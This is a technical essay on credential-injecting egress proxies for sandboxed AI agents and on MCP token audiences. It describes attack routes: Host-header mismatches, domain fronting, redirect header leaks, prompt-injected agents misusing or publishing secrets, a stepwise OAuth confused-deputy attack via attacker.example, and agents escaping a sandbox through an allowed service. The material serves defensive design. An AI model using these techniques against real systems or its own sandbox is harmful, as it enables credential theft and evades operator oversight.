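The steps below are close to those in Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)*, which documents an open-source proxy for the company's Hermes agent.

1. The program asks the proxy for a tunnel to `api.library.example`. The proxy checks that the host is on its allowlist.
2. The program starts a TLS connection through the tunnel. Instead of passing it on, the proxy responds as if it were the library and presents a certificate for `api.library.example` that it has just made.
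3. The program accepts the certificate. Programs trust certificates signed by certain organisations, called certificate authorities, and the operator has added the proxy's own certificate authority to the sandbox's list.
4. The proxy decrypts the request and finds that its domain, method and path match the rule.
5. The proxy opens a second TLS connection, to the real library server, and verifies that server's certificate in the normal way.
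6. It replaces `placeholder-51c8` with the real token and sends the request over the second connection.
7. The library's response returns through the proxy, which encrypts it again for the program.

If the program sent the same request to `attacker.example`, the proxy would refuse the tunnel. Even if the operator allowed that host, no rule would match, so the attacker would receive only the placeholder.

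The certificate authority's private key needs as much protection as the stored secrets, since anyone who has it can impersonate any website to the sandbox. Cloudflare creates a new authority for each sandbox. microsandbox, another open-source sandbox, uses one authority for all sandboxes on a machine by default, according to its *TLS interception* documentation, so a stolen key would affect all of them.

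Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, tested credential injection in a product from their own company, Corvic AI. Code in a sandbox sent GitHub a request without a token, and GitHub responded as if the user had logged in. The code then contacted two echo services, and neither received an `Authorization` header. All 16 of the study's checks gave the secure result.

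In a second run, three echo services also received no credential, but the connection under test never worked because it put the key for an economic data service in a header, while the service expected it in the query string. So we can't tell from that run whether the proxy would have restricted a working credential to one host. Kenney and colleagues also didn't test redirects or DNS rebinding.

### Names that have to match

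A proxy preserves the destination if it contacts the same server that the client named and the policy checked. This is harder to ensure because one request can specify its destination in several places.

| Name | Where it appears |
|---|---|
| Requested host | The URL, or the request for a tunnel |
| TLS server name | The client's first message when it sets up encryption |
| `Host` header | The request inside the encrypted connection |
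| Rule | The proxy's settings |
| Certificate | The real server's reply to the proxy |

Code in the sandbox controls the first three and can make them differ. Suppose the operator also allows `echo.example`, an echo service. The code requests a tunnel to `echo.example` but writes `api.library.example` in the `Host` header. If the proxy chooses its rule from the `Host` header, it attaches the library token and sends it to `echo.example`, which returns it to the code. Checking the certificate doesn't help, because `echo.example` has a valid one for its own name.

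This mistake is easy to make. *How to force AI agents to use an egress proxy*, by simedw, includes a short sample program for the interception tool mitmproxy that adds an Anthropic key when `pretty_host` equals `api.anthropic.com`. mitmproxy's documentation warns that `pretty_host` comes from the `Host` header when one is present, and a client can fake that header. simedw's allowlist would limit the damage, since the tunnel still has to lead to a permitted host.

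The proxy should use the requested host name, and no other, to choose the rule, look up the address and check the certificate. It should refuse the request if the TLS server name or `Host` header differs from that name. microsandbox documents checks of this kind, which work only where it decrypts the traffic.

A faked `Host` header can also get data past an allowlist. In domain fronting, a client requests a tunnel to a permitted site but names a different one in the encrypted request. If one hosting network serves both sites, it may deliver the request to the second. An older Docker page lists domain fronting as a limit of filters that don't inspect traffic.

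Ordinary web servers have the same problem. A June 2026 message on the security mailing list oss-sec describes a request whose URL names one site while its `Host` header names another. NGINX, a popular web server and gateway, applied the first site's access rules. In one common configuration, it then forwarded the request to the server behind it as one for the second site, which only internal users should have been able to reach. NGINX's developers blame the configuration and recommend a different variable, `$host`.

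### Three ways to tell a proxy where to send a request

In the library example, the agent's program used the library's real URL, and a forward proxy left the URL unchanged. Operators can instead have the program call a gateway, or give the agent a tool that takes the target as a parameter.

To use a gateway, the operator changes a program's base URL, the first part of the address it uses for all its requests. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a system for healthcare agents that does this with a sidecar, a small companion program. The agent sends its prompts to `localhost:8443/v1/messages`, an address on its own machine. The sidecar adds the Anthropic key and forwards the prompts to `api.anthropic.com`.

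The agent doesn't specify the address of Anthropic's server, so it can't redirect the request to another one. The sandbox needs no extra certificate authority, because the program is configured to connect to the sidecar. This is the simplest safe design for one provider. It fails if the gateway takes an address from the request, as LiteLLM did, or if somebody changes the base URL to an address outside the gateway.

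A gateway for several providers also needs exact routing. Aikido's *http-proxy-middleware is vulnerable to Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* describes a JavaScript package that chose a destination by looking for a configured name anywhere in the request's host and URL. A request with a crafted `Host` header could match the wrong entry in the operator's table and go to that entry's server. The developers fixed this by requiring the whole host name to match.

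Responses can also cause a client to bypass a gateway, because services often return full URLs, such as a link to the next page of results. A program that follows such a link contacts the provider directly unless the gateway rewrites the link. A forward proxy doesn't have this problem because the program sends it requests for every host.

The third design is a tool that takes a complete URL, like a fetch tool, and adds a credential. Mintlify's *token injection* documents one called `fetch_external`. The agent gives it a GitHub URL and a method. The tool extracts the host name and checks it against an allowlist before looking up a token.

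Such a tool writes the `Host` header and TLS server name itself, so the agent can't make them differ unless it can also set headers. But if the tool checks the URL with one parser and connects with another, it can repeat the bracket error that let a fetch server reach internal addresses. A tool that checks only the host name, and not the scheme or port, could also send a token over unencrypted `http` or to another program on the same server. Firewalls can't easily catch these errors, because all the connections they inspect come from the tool.

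| Design | Who names the server | How the destination can change |
|---|---|---|
| Forward proxy | The client, in the URL or tunnel request | The proxy chooses a rule from a different name |
| Gateway | The operator, in the gateway's settings | The caller overrides the address, loose matching picks the wrong server, or the base URL changes |
| Target as a parameter | The caller, in an argument | The tool checks one reading of the URL and contacts another |

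A forward proxy suits agents that use many services through ordinary software, because the only change that software needs is to trust the certificate authority. A tool with a URL parameter is reasonable when the agent makes only simple requests and the operator controls the tool's code.

### When a redirect moves the credential

A server that legitimately receives a credential can still redirect the client elsewhere. When a proxy injects the credential, what happens next depends on which program follows the redirect.

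Suppose `api.library.example` redirects the reservation to `files.example`. If the proxy returns the redirect to the agent's program, the program makes a new request, which the proxy checks against its rules. No rule covers `files.example`, so the token stays in the proxy. If the proxy adds the token and then follows the redirect itself, it may send the token to `files.example` too. Proxies should therefore return redirects without following them.

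Tokenizer needs its host list even when nobody has attacked the application. A program that follows a redirect through Tokenizer may resend its `Proxy-Tokenizer` header, which most HTTP libraries wouldn't recognise as sensitive. If the secret had no host list, Tokenizer would decrypt the secret and send it to the new host.

HTTP libraries have mishandled redirects for years. A 2022 report in BugBoard's *Credential leak on redirect* describes how curl, a widely used download tool, removed the standard login headers when redirected to another host but still sent a custom one called `x-auth-token`. Cloudflare's example code puts its secret in a header with the same name, so anyone adapting it should check whether their code follows redirects.

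Checking the address of every redirect doesn't stop credentials from leaking to another host. The Ruby library ssrf_filter is meant to block requests to internal addresses, but argareksapatii (2026) showed in *Authorization header leak in ssrf_filter via cross-host redirect* that it copied the caller's original headers into each redirected request. The library sent a bearer token to a second host, where argareksapatii captured it and used it successfully.

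Comparing only host names isn't enough either. CodexBar, an app that queries AI providers, could send cookies, tokens and API keys to a different port, or to the same host over unencrypted `http`. OSV's *CVE-2026-49949* (2026) lists version 0.33.0 as the fix. A client should drop its credentials if the scheme, host or port changes.

The credential a client sends to its proxy can also leak. The JavaScript library Axios adds a `Proxy-Authorization` header when it uses a proxy with a password. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-44486* (2026), if a redirect led to a host that Axios contacted directly, Axios could send the header to that host. Corgea's *@hapi/wreck leaks sensitive `Proxy-Authorization` header across cross-hostname redirects* reports a similar flaw in another library, which removed `Authorization` and `Cookie` but not `Proxy-Authorization`.

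In simedw's system, that header holds a short-lived token that identifies the agent's run and its permissions. A stranger who obtained the token would also need to reach the proxy to use it. Nous Research reduces this risk by making its proxy listen only on addresses that other machines can't contact.

### Using a key without holding it

Credential injection stops an agent from copying a token, but the agent can still use it. If instructions on a web page led the library agent to reserve 50 books, the proxy would add the token to all 50 requests and so act as a confused deputy.

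ZenML's tutorial *Credential proxy* includes a working demonstration in which the proxy adds a token to every request for a private wiki, whatever the path or method. The tutorial recommends tighter rules for real systems.

Rules like those in fnox help when different actions have different paths or methods. The sandbox firewall from the hosting company Vercel also supports such rules. Tuttle (2026), in *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox*, gives the example of code that may submit results to one address but may not read anything else from the same service. But some services use one path for every action and specify the action in the request body. The operator then needs a proxy that can parse that service's requests, or a token with fewer permissions.

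Kenney and colleagues scored eight threats before and after adding their vault, multiplying likelihood by impact, each rated from one to five. The score for a secret pasted into a prompt fell from 25 to 4, while the score for a connection with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15. The scores are the researchers' judgements of their own company's product, but it makes sense that the second fell less, because a token that can delete a repository can still do so when a proxy holds it.

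### Hosts that return the secret

A host list ensures that only the listed hosts receive a key, but one of them may send it back in a test page or error message that repeats the request's headers. Varlock's *Credential proxy*, the documentation for another open-source tool, warns that an agent with access to such a page can recover the key.

Varlock searches responses for the secret and replaces it with the placeholder. It finds only exact matches in uncompressed text of up to 2 MB, so the agent's program can avoid the search by requesting a compressed response. Varlock's documentation accordingly treats the search as an extra precaution and advises users to give secrets only to hosts that won't return them.

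A proxy that replaces placeholders in too many places can also publish a secret. Docker's experimental option for custom secrets replaces the placeholder anywhere in a request to the chosen domain, including the body. If that domain hosts a public forum, an injected instruction could make the agent post a comment containing the placeholder, and the proxy would replace it with the real secret. fnox prevents this by replacing the placeholder only in the place specified in its rule.

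Keys in URLs also need care, because the server that receives the URL may log it. For example, Google's Gemini service accepts its key in the query string, and the proxy from Nous Research can insert the real key there.

### Connections that avoid the proxy

Programs usually find a proxy through environment variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, but they can ignore them. As simedw shows, a few lines of Python can open a direct connection instead. A program that does this won't have a real key, since only the proxy adds it, but it can send any other data it has.

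simedw's first repair was a Docker network with no direct route to the internet. That still left code in the sandbox able to reach Docker's DNS service and possibly other programs on the host computer. The final version has firewall rules that accept connections from the sandbox only to the proxy's address and port. It drops DNS traffic, and the proxy looks up names and checks the addresses itself.

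Other products have gaps that depend on the kind of traffic:

- Cloudflare's *outbound traffic* explains that only connections to ports 80 and 443 pass through the operator's program.
- Docker's *Isolation layers* describes two proxies, one for programs that use the proxy settings and one that catches other connections. Both enforce the network policy, but only the first adds credentials.
- Freestyle's *inspect sandbox traffic with mitmproxy* blocks UDP traffic on port 443, because the newest version of HTTP uses it and would otherwise avoid inspection.

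Tools that run on the same computer and user account as the agent leave a bigger security gap. Varlock and fnox both warn that such an agent could start a program outside the proxy's control and read the secrets from wherever they are stored. Their users also need a container or virtual machine, at least for an agent that reads web pages.

A flaw in a permitted service can also let an agent out of its sandbox. Forlini (2026), in *Hugging Face drops in-depth hack report, while OpenAI gives us 7 bullets*, reports that OpenAI agents reached the open internet in July 2026 by exploiting the package-cache service that their sandbox allowed them to use.

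### A proxy that holds every key

Moving keys out of many sandboxes and into one proxy gives attackers a more valuable target. The secrets manager Infisical offers a proxy that can serve agents across an organisation. It checks which services each agent may use, then fetches the real secrets with its own identity. Someone who took over that proxy could presumably fetch all those secrets.

Tokenizer limits this risk better because the proxy can use a secret only after receiving it in encrypted form. An attacker inside Tokenizer could still collect secrets as requests came in, but couldn't take those the application had not used. Running a separate proxy for each agent also limits the damage, but leaves more proxies to maintain.

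As Freestyle's guide notes, a proxy that decrypts traffic has access to passwords, cookies and the contents of every request, as well as keys. To keep this data out of its log, fnox records only the method, domain, path and the name of the secret, which is enough to investigate most problems.

### Leaving the connection encrypted

The alternative is a forward proxy that opens an encrypted tunnel and lets the client keep its own key.

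| | Proxy adds the key | Client keeps the key in a tunnel |
|---|---|---|
| Can code in the sandbox copy the key? | Only if a host returns it | Yes |
| What can the proxy read? | Everything | The host and port |
| Can the proxy restrict paths and methods? | Yes | No |
| Who checks the real server's certificate? | The proxy | The client |

For an agent that reads untrusted pages, having the proxy add the key is usually better than tunneling encrypted traffic from the sandbox. A key in the sandbox can leak through any permitted host that forwards data, and the proxy can't detect it inside an encrypted request. The tunnel makes sense when the operator shouldn't read the traffic, or when the key expires quickly and permits very little.

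Whether a proxy can add credentials sometimes depends on the program making the request. Some programs accept only a particular certificate and reject the one the proxy makes. Others prove their identity with their own certificate, which microsandbox's proxy can't present for them. The Nous Research proxy can't handle Amazon's keys, because programs use them to sign each request and never send them. By the time the proxy could replace a placeholder key, the program would already have signed the request with it. The proxy would have to sign the request itself, and until it can, the sandbox must hold a real key.

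Docker keeps SSH keys outside the sandbox without decrypting the connection. Developers often use SSH to connect to servers, and it lets them log in by using a private key to sign a challenge from the server. Docker leaves the private key on the developer's computer and lets programs in the sandbox request signatures. These programs can't copy the key, but any of them can log in with it as long as the sandbox can request signatures.

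Operators can also use both arrangements at once. Tuttle explains that Vercel's firewall decrypts only connections to hosts whose rules require it. For other permitted hosts, it reads the TLS server name, checks the name and the IP address against its policies, and leaves the encryption intact. Such a firewall must also confirm that the address belongs to that name. Otherwise, code in the sandbox could give the name of a permitted host while connecting to an attacker's server.

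## The Model Context Protocol's rule against passing tokens on

An injecting proxy adds a key that its client doesn't have. A program can also forward a credential from its client to another service. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) forbids its servers to do this. *Authorization* (2026), its specification for access tokens, bars servers from accepting or forwarding any token that isn't valid for their own resources. Forward proxies, however, routinely carry their clients' credentials to other servers. To see why that is safe, we need to know which service each token is for.

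### Tokens and their audiences

Suppose Nadia asks an agent on her laptop to move a meeting. The agent's software, the MCP client, calls a tool on an MCP server that a scheduling company runs at `mcp.example.com`. That server calls the calendar service at `cal.example.com`, where Nadia has an account, and must prove that it may act for her.

MCP uses OAuth, a standard that lets people give a program access to an account without giving it their password. The user logs in at an authorization server and approves the request, and the authorization server issues an access token to the program. The token's audience is the service for which the authorization server issued it. Campbell, Bradley and Tschofenig, in *RFC 8707*, an OAuth standard, give an example token for a calendar service. Decoded, it contains:

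```
iss:    http://authorization-server.example.com
sub:    __b_c
exp:    1588420800
scope:  calendar
aud:    https://cal.example.com/
```

The fields specify the issuer, user, expiry time, permissions and audience. The issuer signs the token, so nobody else can change the audience without invalidating the signature.

The March 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol (2025) required servers to validate tokens but had no rule about audiences. The June 2025 revision (Model Context Protocol, 2025) added the audience check and the ban on forwarding tokens. The current revision, dated 28 July 2026, keeps both.

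The rule has limits. Authorization is optional in MCP, so a server with no login can comply. Local servers that communicate with the client through standard input and output should take credentials from their environment instead.

### If the server forwards a calendar token

The easiest way to build Nadia's server is to have the client obtain a calendar token and send it with each tool call. The server copies the token into its own request to the calendar service, which moves the meeting. The developer doesn't have to write any login code. The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* calls this "token passthrough" and lists several problems with it.

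Suppose the MCP server lets each client delete at most ten events a day. A client with a calendar token can skip the MCP server and delete as many events as the calendar service allows.

The logs also become misleading. The calendar service's log may attribute the request to the agent's software, which obtained the token, although the MCP server sent it. The MCP server may be unable to read a token meant for another service, in which case it can't identify the client calling it. If a bug in the server deleted Nadia's events, an investigator would probably start by checking the agent's software instead.

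Finally, a token stolen in one place can be used in another. If an attacker steals Nadia's calendar token from a meeting-room display and the MCP server accepts it, the attacker can use the server's tools as Nadia, including those unrelated to her calendar.

The last problem can arise even if the server never forwards a token. Suppose a quiz app's operator receives tokens from users who log in through the same authorization server. If Nadia's MCP server doesn't check a token's audience, the operator can present her quiz token to it.

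### A separate token for each service

In the permitted flow, the MCP server accepts one token and uses another:

1. The client calls the MCP server without a token. The server refuses and returns a URL with details of its authorization server. (A malicious server could supply an internal address here, so clients need the same address checks as fetch servers.)
2. The client opens that authorization server in Nadia's browser and names `https://mcp.example.com` as the service it wants to use.
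3. Nadia approves. The authorization server sends her browser back to the client with a short-lived code, which the client exchanges for the first token.
4. The client calls the tool with this token, and the MCP server checks that the token is for `mcp.example.com`.
5. The MCP server sends Nadia to the calendar's own authorization server. She approves, and the MCP server receives a second token.
6. The MCP server calls the calendar service with the second token.

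Later calls need only steps 4 and 6 until a token expires. The November 2025 revision of the Model Context Protocol (2025) added URL mode elicitation, which helps with step 5 by letting a server ask the user to open a web page, such as a login page.

| | First token | Second token |
|---|---|---|
| Audience | The MCP server | The calendar service |
| Program that obtained it | The MCP client | The MCP server |
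| What it permits | Use of the MCP server's tools | Access to Nadia's calendar |

The client can't use the first token at the calendar service, so it can't bypass the MCP server's limits. The calendar service can identify the MCP server in its log, and Nadia can withdraw the server's access without affecting other programs. A token stolen from the meeting-room display fails the check in step 4.

### How a client names the audience

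In step 2, the client names the service with the `resource` parameter from RFC 8707:

`resource=https%3A%2F%2Fmcp.example.com`

The authorization server should then restrict the token to that service. Campbell and colleagues also show how a client with permission for both a calendar and an address book can request a separate token for each. A single token with two audiences would be riskier, because either service could use it to access the other.

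The parameter also protects clients from malicious MCP servers. Suppose an MCP server at `attacker.example` directs Nadia's client to her calendar's authorization server. Without the parameter, the client might obtain a token that works for the calendar and give it to the attacker. The parameter tells the authorization server that the token is for `attacker.example`, so it can refuse the request or issue a token that the calendar service won't accept.

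This works only if the authorization server supports the parameter. MCP clients must send it regardless, and may not be able to tell whether it had any effect. *OAuth 2.0 Resource Parameter in Access Token Response* (McGuinness, Hanson and Skokan, 2026), which is still a draft, proposes that the authorization server name the resource when it returns the token, so that the client can check.

An audience check doesn't replace Tokenizer's list of hosts, which keeps tokens from reaching an attacker. The audience only limits where a stolen token works. If somebody sends a calendar token to `attacker.example`, the attacker can still use it at the calendar service, because that service is the token's correct audience.

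The Model Context Protocol (2026) revision applies similar checks to authorization servers. A client may use several, and a malicious one could trick it into handing over an authorization code from an honest one. If the response names its issuer, the client must now check that name against the authorization server it meant to use. It must also never use credentials from one authorization server with another. The revision also removes sessions from the protocol. MCP servers that need to keep data between calls now give the client an identifier, such as a shopping cart number, but must not accept it as proof of who is calling.

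### Exchanging one token for another

In step 5, Nadia had to log in a second time. Token exchange, defined by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *RFC 8693*, can avoid this. The MCP server sends Nadia's first token to an authorization server and requests one for the calendar service. In outline:

```
subject_token:  (the token Nadia's client sent)
actor_token:    (proof of the MCP server's identity, optional)
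resource:       https://cal.example.com/
scope:          calendar
```

The new token can name both Nadia and the MCP server. Jones calls this delegation in an earlier draft, because the server is still clearly acting for her. In impersonation, the server would be indistinguishable from Nadia.

The authorization server has to recognise the first token and be allowed to issue tokens for the calendar. That is realistic inside a company that runs its own login system, but much less likely when the MCP server and the calendar belong to unrelated companies. In that case, the MCP server needs the second login.

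Token exchange also needs rules about who may use it. If any program could exchange any token, someone who stole Nadia's first token could use it to get a calendar token. Authlete's *RFC 8693 OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* points out that the standard leaves details necessary for security to the implementer. Descope, a vendor of login software, adds that an exchange doesn't cancel the original token, so a stolen one stays valid until it expires or somebody revokes it.

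### Reusing a user's earlier consent

A server can keep its tokens separate and still give an attacker access. The guidance describes a confused deputy attack on MCP proxy servers, which connect clients to another company's service. Such a server often registers once with the other service and uses the same client ID for everyone. All requests to the calendar service then carry the ID `mcp-proxy`, whichever client started them.

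After Nadia approves `mcp-proxy` for the first time, the calendar's authorization server stores a cookie in her browser so that it needn't ask again. The attack uses that cookie:

1. The attacker registers a new client with the MCP server, which accepts registrations automatically, and gives an address on `attacker.example` for receiving codes.
2. The attacker sends Nadia a link that starts a login for this client.
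3. Nadia clicks it, and her browser arrives at the calendar's authorization server with a request from `mcp-proxy`.
4. The authorization server finds the cookie and approves the request without asking her.
5. The MCP server receives a calendar token for Nadia, creates a code for its own service and sends her browser to `attacker.example` with that code.
6. The attacker exchanges the code for a token and uses the calendar tools as Nadia.

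An audience check wouldn't help, because both tokens go to the right services. PKCE, an OAuth safeguard, wouldn't help either. It requires the program that starts a login to present a matching secret to redeem the code, but here the attacker started the login and has the secret.

Nadia agreed to let the MCP server access her calendar, and the attacker used that consent for a different client. The MCP server therefore has to ask for her consent separately for each client before it sends the browser to the calendar's authorization server. Its consent page must show the client's name, the permissions requested and the address that will receive the authorization code. The server must remember her approval for that client ID only, because a cookie that didn't identify the client would allow the same attack. It must set the cookie that tracks the login only after she approves, or an attacker could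 bypass the consent page.

The page still helps only if Nadia reads it. An attacker can register a client under a familiar name, so the address is a more useful clue than the name. Judging by Anthropic's tests of permission prompts, many people would miss it.

Since November 2025, MCP has recommended a different form of registration, in which a client's ID is the `https` address of a document describing it. The July 2026 revision deprecates automatic registration in favour of this method. It makes impersonation harder because an attacker can't publish a document on another company's domain. Servers still need to ask users about each client, since an attacker can register one using a document on their own domain.

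### When forwarding a credential is sound

Suppose Nadia's agent calls the calendar service directly and her employer's forward proxy carries the request. The client addressed the request to `cal.example.com`, which is the token's audience, and the proxy delivers it there. The proxy doesn't need to be the audience itself because it only carries the request. If the client uses an encrypted tunnel, the proxy can't read the token. Any login the proxy requires goes in the separate `Proxy-Authorization` header.

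An MCP server differs because the client addresses its request to the server. The server interprets the call to move a meeting and writes a new request, perhaps to a service that the client has no information about. The server is therefore an audience itself and needs its own token.

An intermediary should forward a token only if the server the client named, the token's audience and the server that receives the token all match.

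| Intermediary | Server the client named | Token's audience | Server that receives the token | Sound? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Forward proxy | Calendar | Calendar | Calendar | Yes |
| Load balancer for the MCP server | MCP server | MCP server | MCP server | Yes |
| MCP server forwarding a calendar token | MCP server | Calendar | Calendar | No |
| MCP server forwarding its own token | MCP server | MCP server | Calendar | No |

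A load balancer, which spreads requests over several copies of a server, can safely pass the token on because the balancer belongs to the service that the client named. A proxy that decrypts traffic can also forward a token safely, but only if it contacts the host that the client requested and its operator is trustworthy.

This comparison doesn't work for ordinary API keys, which usually don't name an audience. The key's owner has to approve the destination instead, as customers do when they give LiteLLM their own keys for a particular provider.

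### How deployed servers comply

*A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (Zhou, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), the largest relevant study, found 7,973 live servers on the public internet but didn't measure token passthrough. Of these servers, 40.55% required no authentication, 30.45% used OAuth and 29.00% used fixed tokens or API keys. Most of the open servers the researchers sampled seemed to be tests or demonstrations, but one exposed more than 5,000 internal customer records.

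The researchers tested 119 of the OAuth servers in detail and found at least one flaw in every one. In 114, anyone could register a client with any address for receiving codes. In 72, the consent page didn't show that address. These rates may not apply to other OAuth servers, because the researchers chose only servers that accepted automatic registration.

The results do show that the conditions for the consent attack are common. Of the 119 servers, 81 connected users to another service and only five restricted the addresses, so at least 76 of the 81 would have let an attacker register one. Zhou and colleagues don't report how many of the 76 also used one shared client ID, relied on remembered consent and failed to ask about each client, so we can't tell how many were vulnerable.

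They did find a related flaw in seven servers. The servers put the client's return address into a value that passed through the user's browser, and didn't check it afterwards, so an attacker could change the address and receive the code.

There is less evidence about audience checks. WorkOS (2026), which sells login services, writes that both the `resource` parameter and audience checks are "still widely omitted", but gives no figure. *A Taxonomy of Runtime Faults in Model Context Protocol Servers* (2026) classifies forwarding tokens without proper verification as a fault. It also describes a server that refused requests because a field in the token didn't match. Such failures give developers a reason to remove the check.

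Glama's *ADR-005* records a decision to remove token passthrough from an MCP server for the file-sharing software Nextcloud. The server's developers planned to replace it with token exchange and tokens with several audiences. Token exchange fits the specification well. A token valid for both the MCP server and Nextcloud would pass an audience check at each, but a server that forwarded it would still break the rule, which requires a separate token for the second service.

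Hosting companies may be able to improve compliance faster than individual developers. *Characterizing Network Centralization and Observability in the Remote MCP Ecosystem* (2026) found that 35% of servers hosted elsewhere allowed access without authentication, but none of those hosted by the company Smithery did. Smithery puts an OAuth login in front of every server it hosts, so its customers don't have to build one. That login protects access to the MCP server but doesn't show how the server obtains tokens for other services.

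### Objections to the cost

Using separate tokens takes much more work than forwarding one. peteski22 (2025), in *MCP's Identity Crisis*, argues that every server would need its own login pages, token storage and renewal, and that developers avoid this work by using fixed credentials. The essay's examples are the official servers from Grafana, GitHub and Stripe. Each receives a key when it starts, so each process serves only one identity.

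Those examples are weaker evidence than they seem, because under the specification local servers should take credentials from their environment. But they do support the complaint about the rule's burden. *Experiences with Model Context Protocol Servers for Science and High Performance Computing* (2025) reports that handling OAuth tokens in hosted servers added complexity, and that the research team ran its servers in each user's own environment instead. This works for one researcher but not for a company that wants one server for thousands of employees.

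peteski22 also points out that scheduled jobs can't open a browser, and that company networks may block the login pages of outside services. Consent in advance solves part of the first problem, since a server can often renew a token without the user. It doesn't help if the network blocks the authorization server.

The essay proposes "validated passthrough", in which the server checks that a token is genuine and intended for the other service before forwarding it, as API gateways commonly do. The check would stop the quiz app's operator, but a client could still bypass the MCP server and use the token directly, and the logs would still be misleading. An API gateway usually belongs to the company whose service it protects, but Nadia's scheduling company is not affiliated with her calendar service.

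The essay's best question is why anyone would trust an MCP server with private data but not with a token. The permitted flow does trust the server with a calendar token, but the calendar service issues that token specifically to the MCP server, with permissions Nadia approved for it, and can revoke it separately. Although these controls are useful, the scheduling company may have to store calendar tokens for all its users, which passthrough avoids. That storage makes its server a more attractive target.

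Token exchange can avoid it too, because the server can request a short-lived calendar token for each call and then discard it. Token exchange also suits companies that already run a central login system, and it doesn't require a browser for every service. But according to tianpan.co's *OAuth in MCP* (2026), a request for explicit support in MCP was still open in May 2026, and companies were improvising their own versions.
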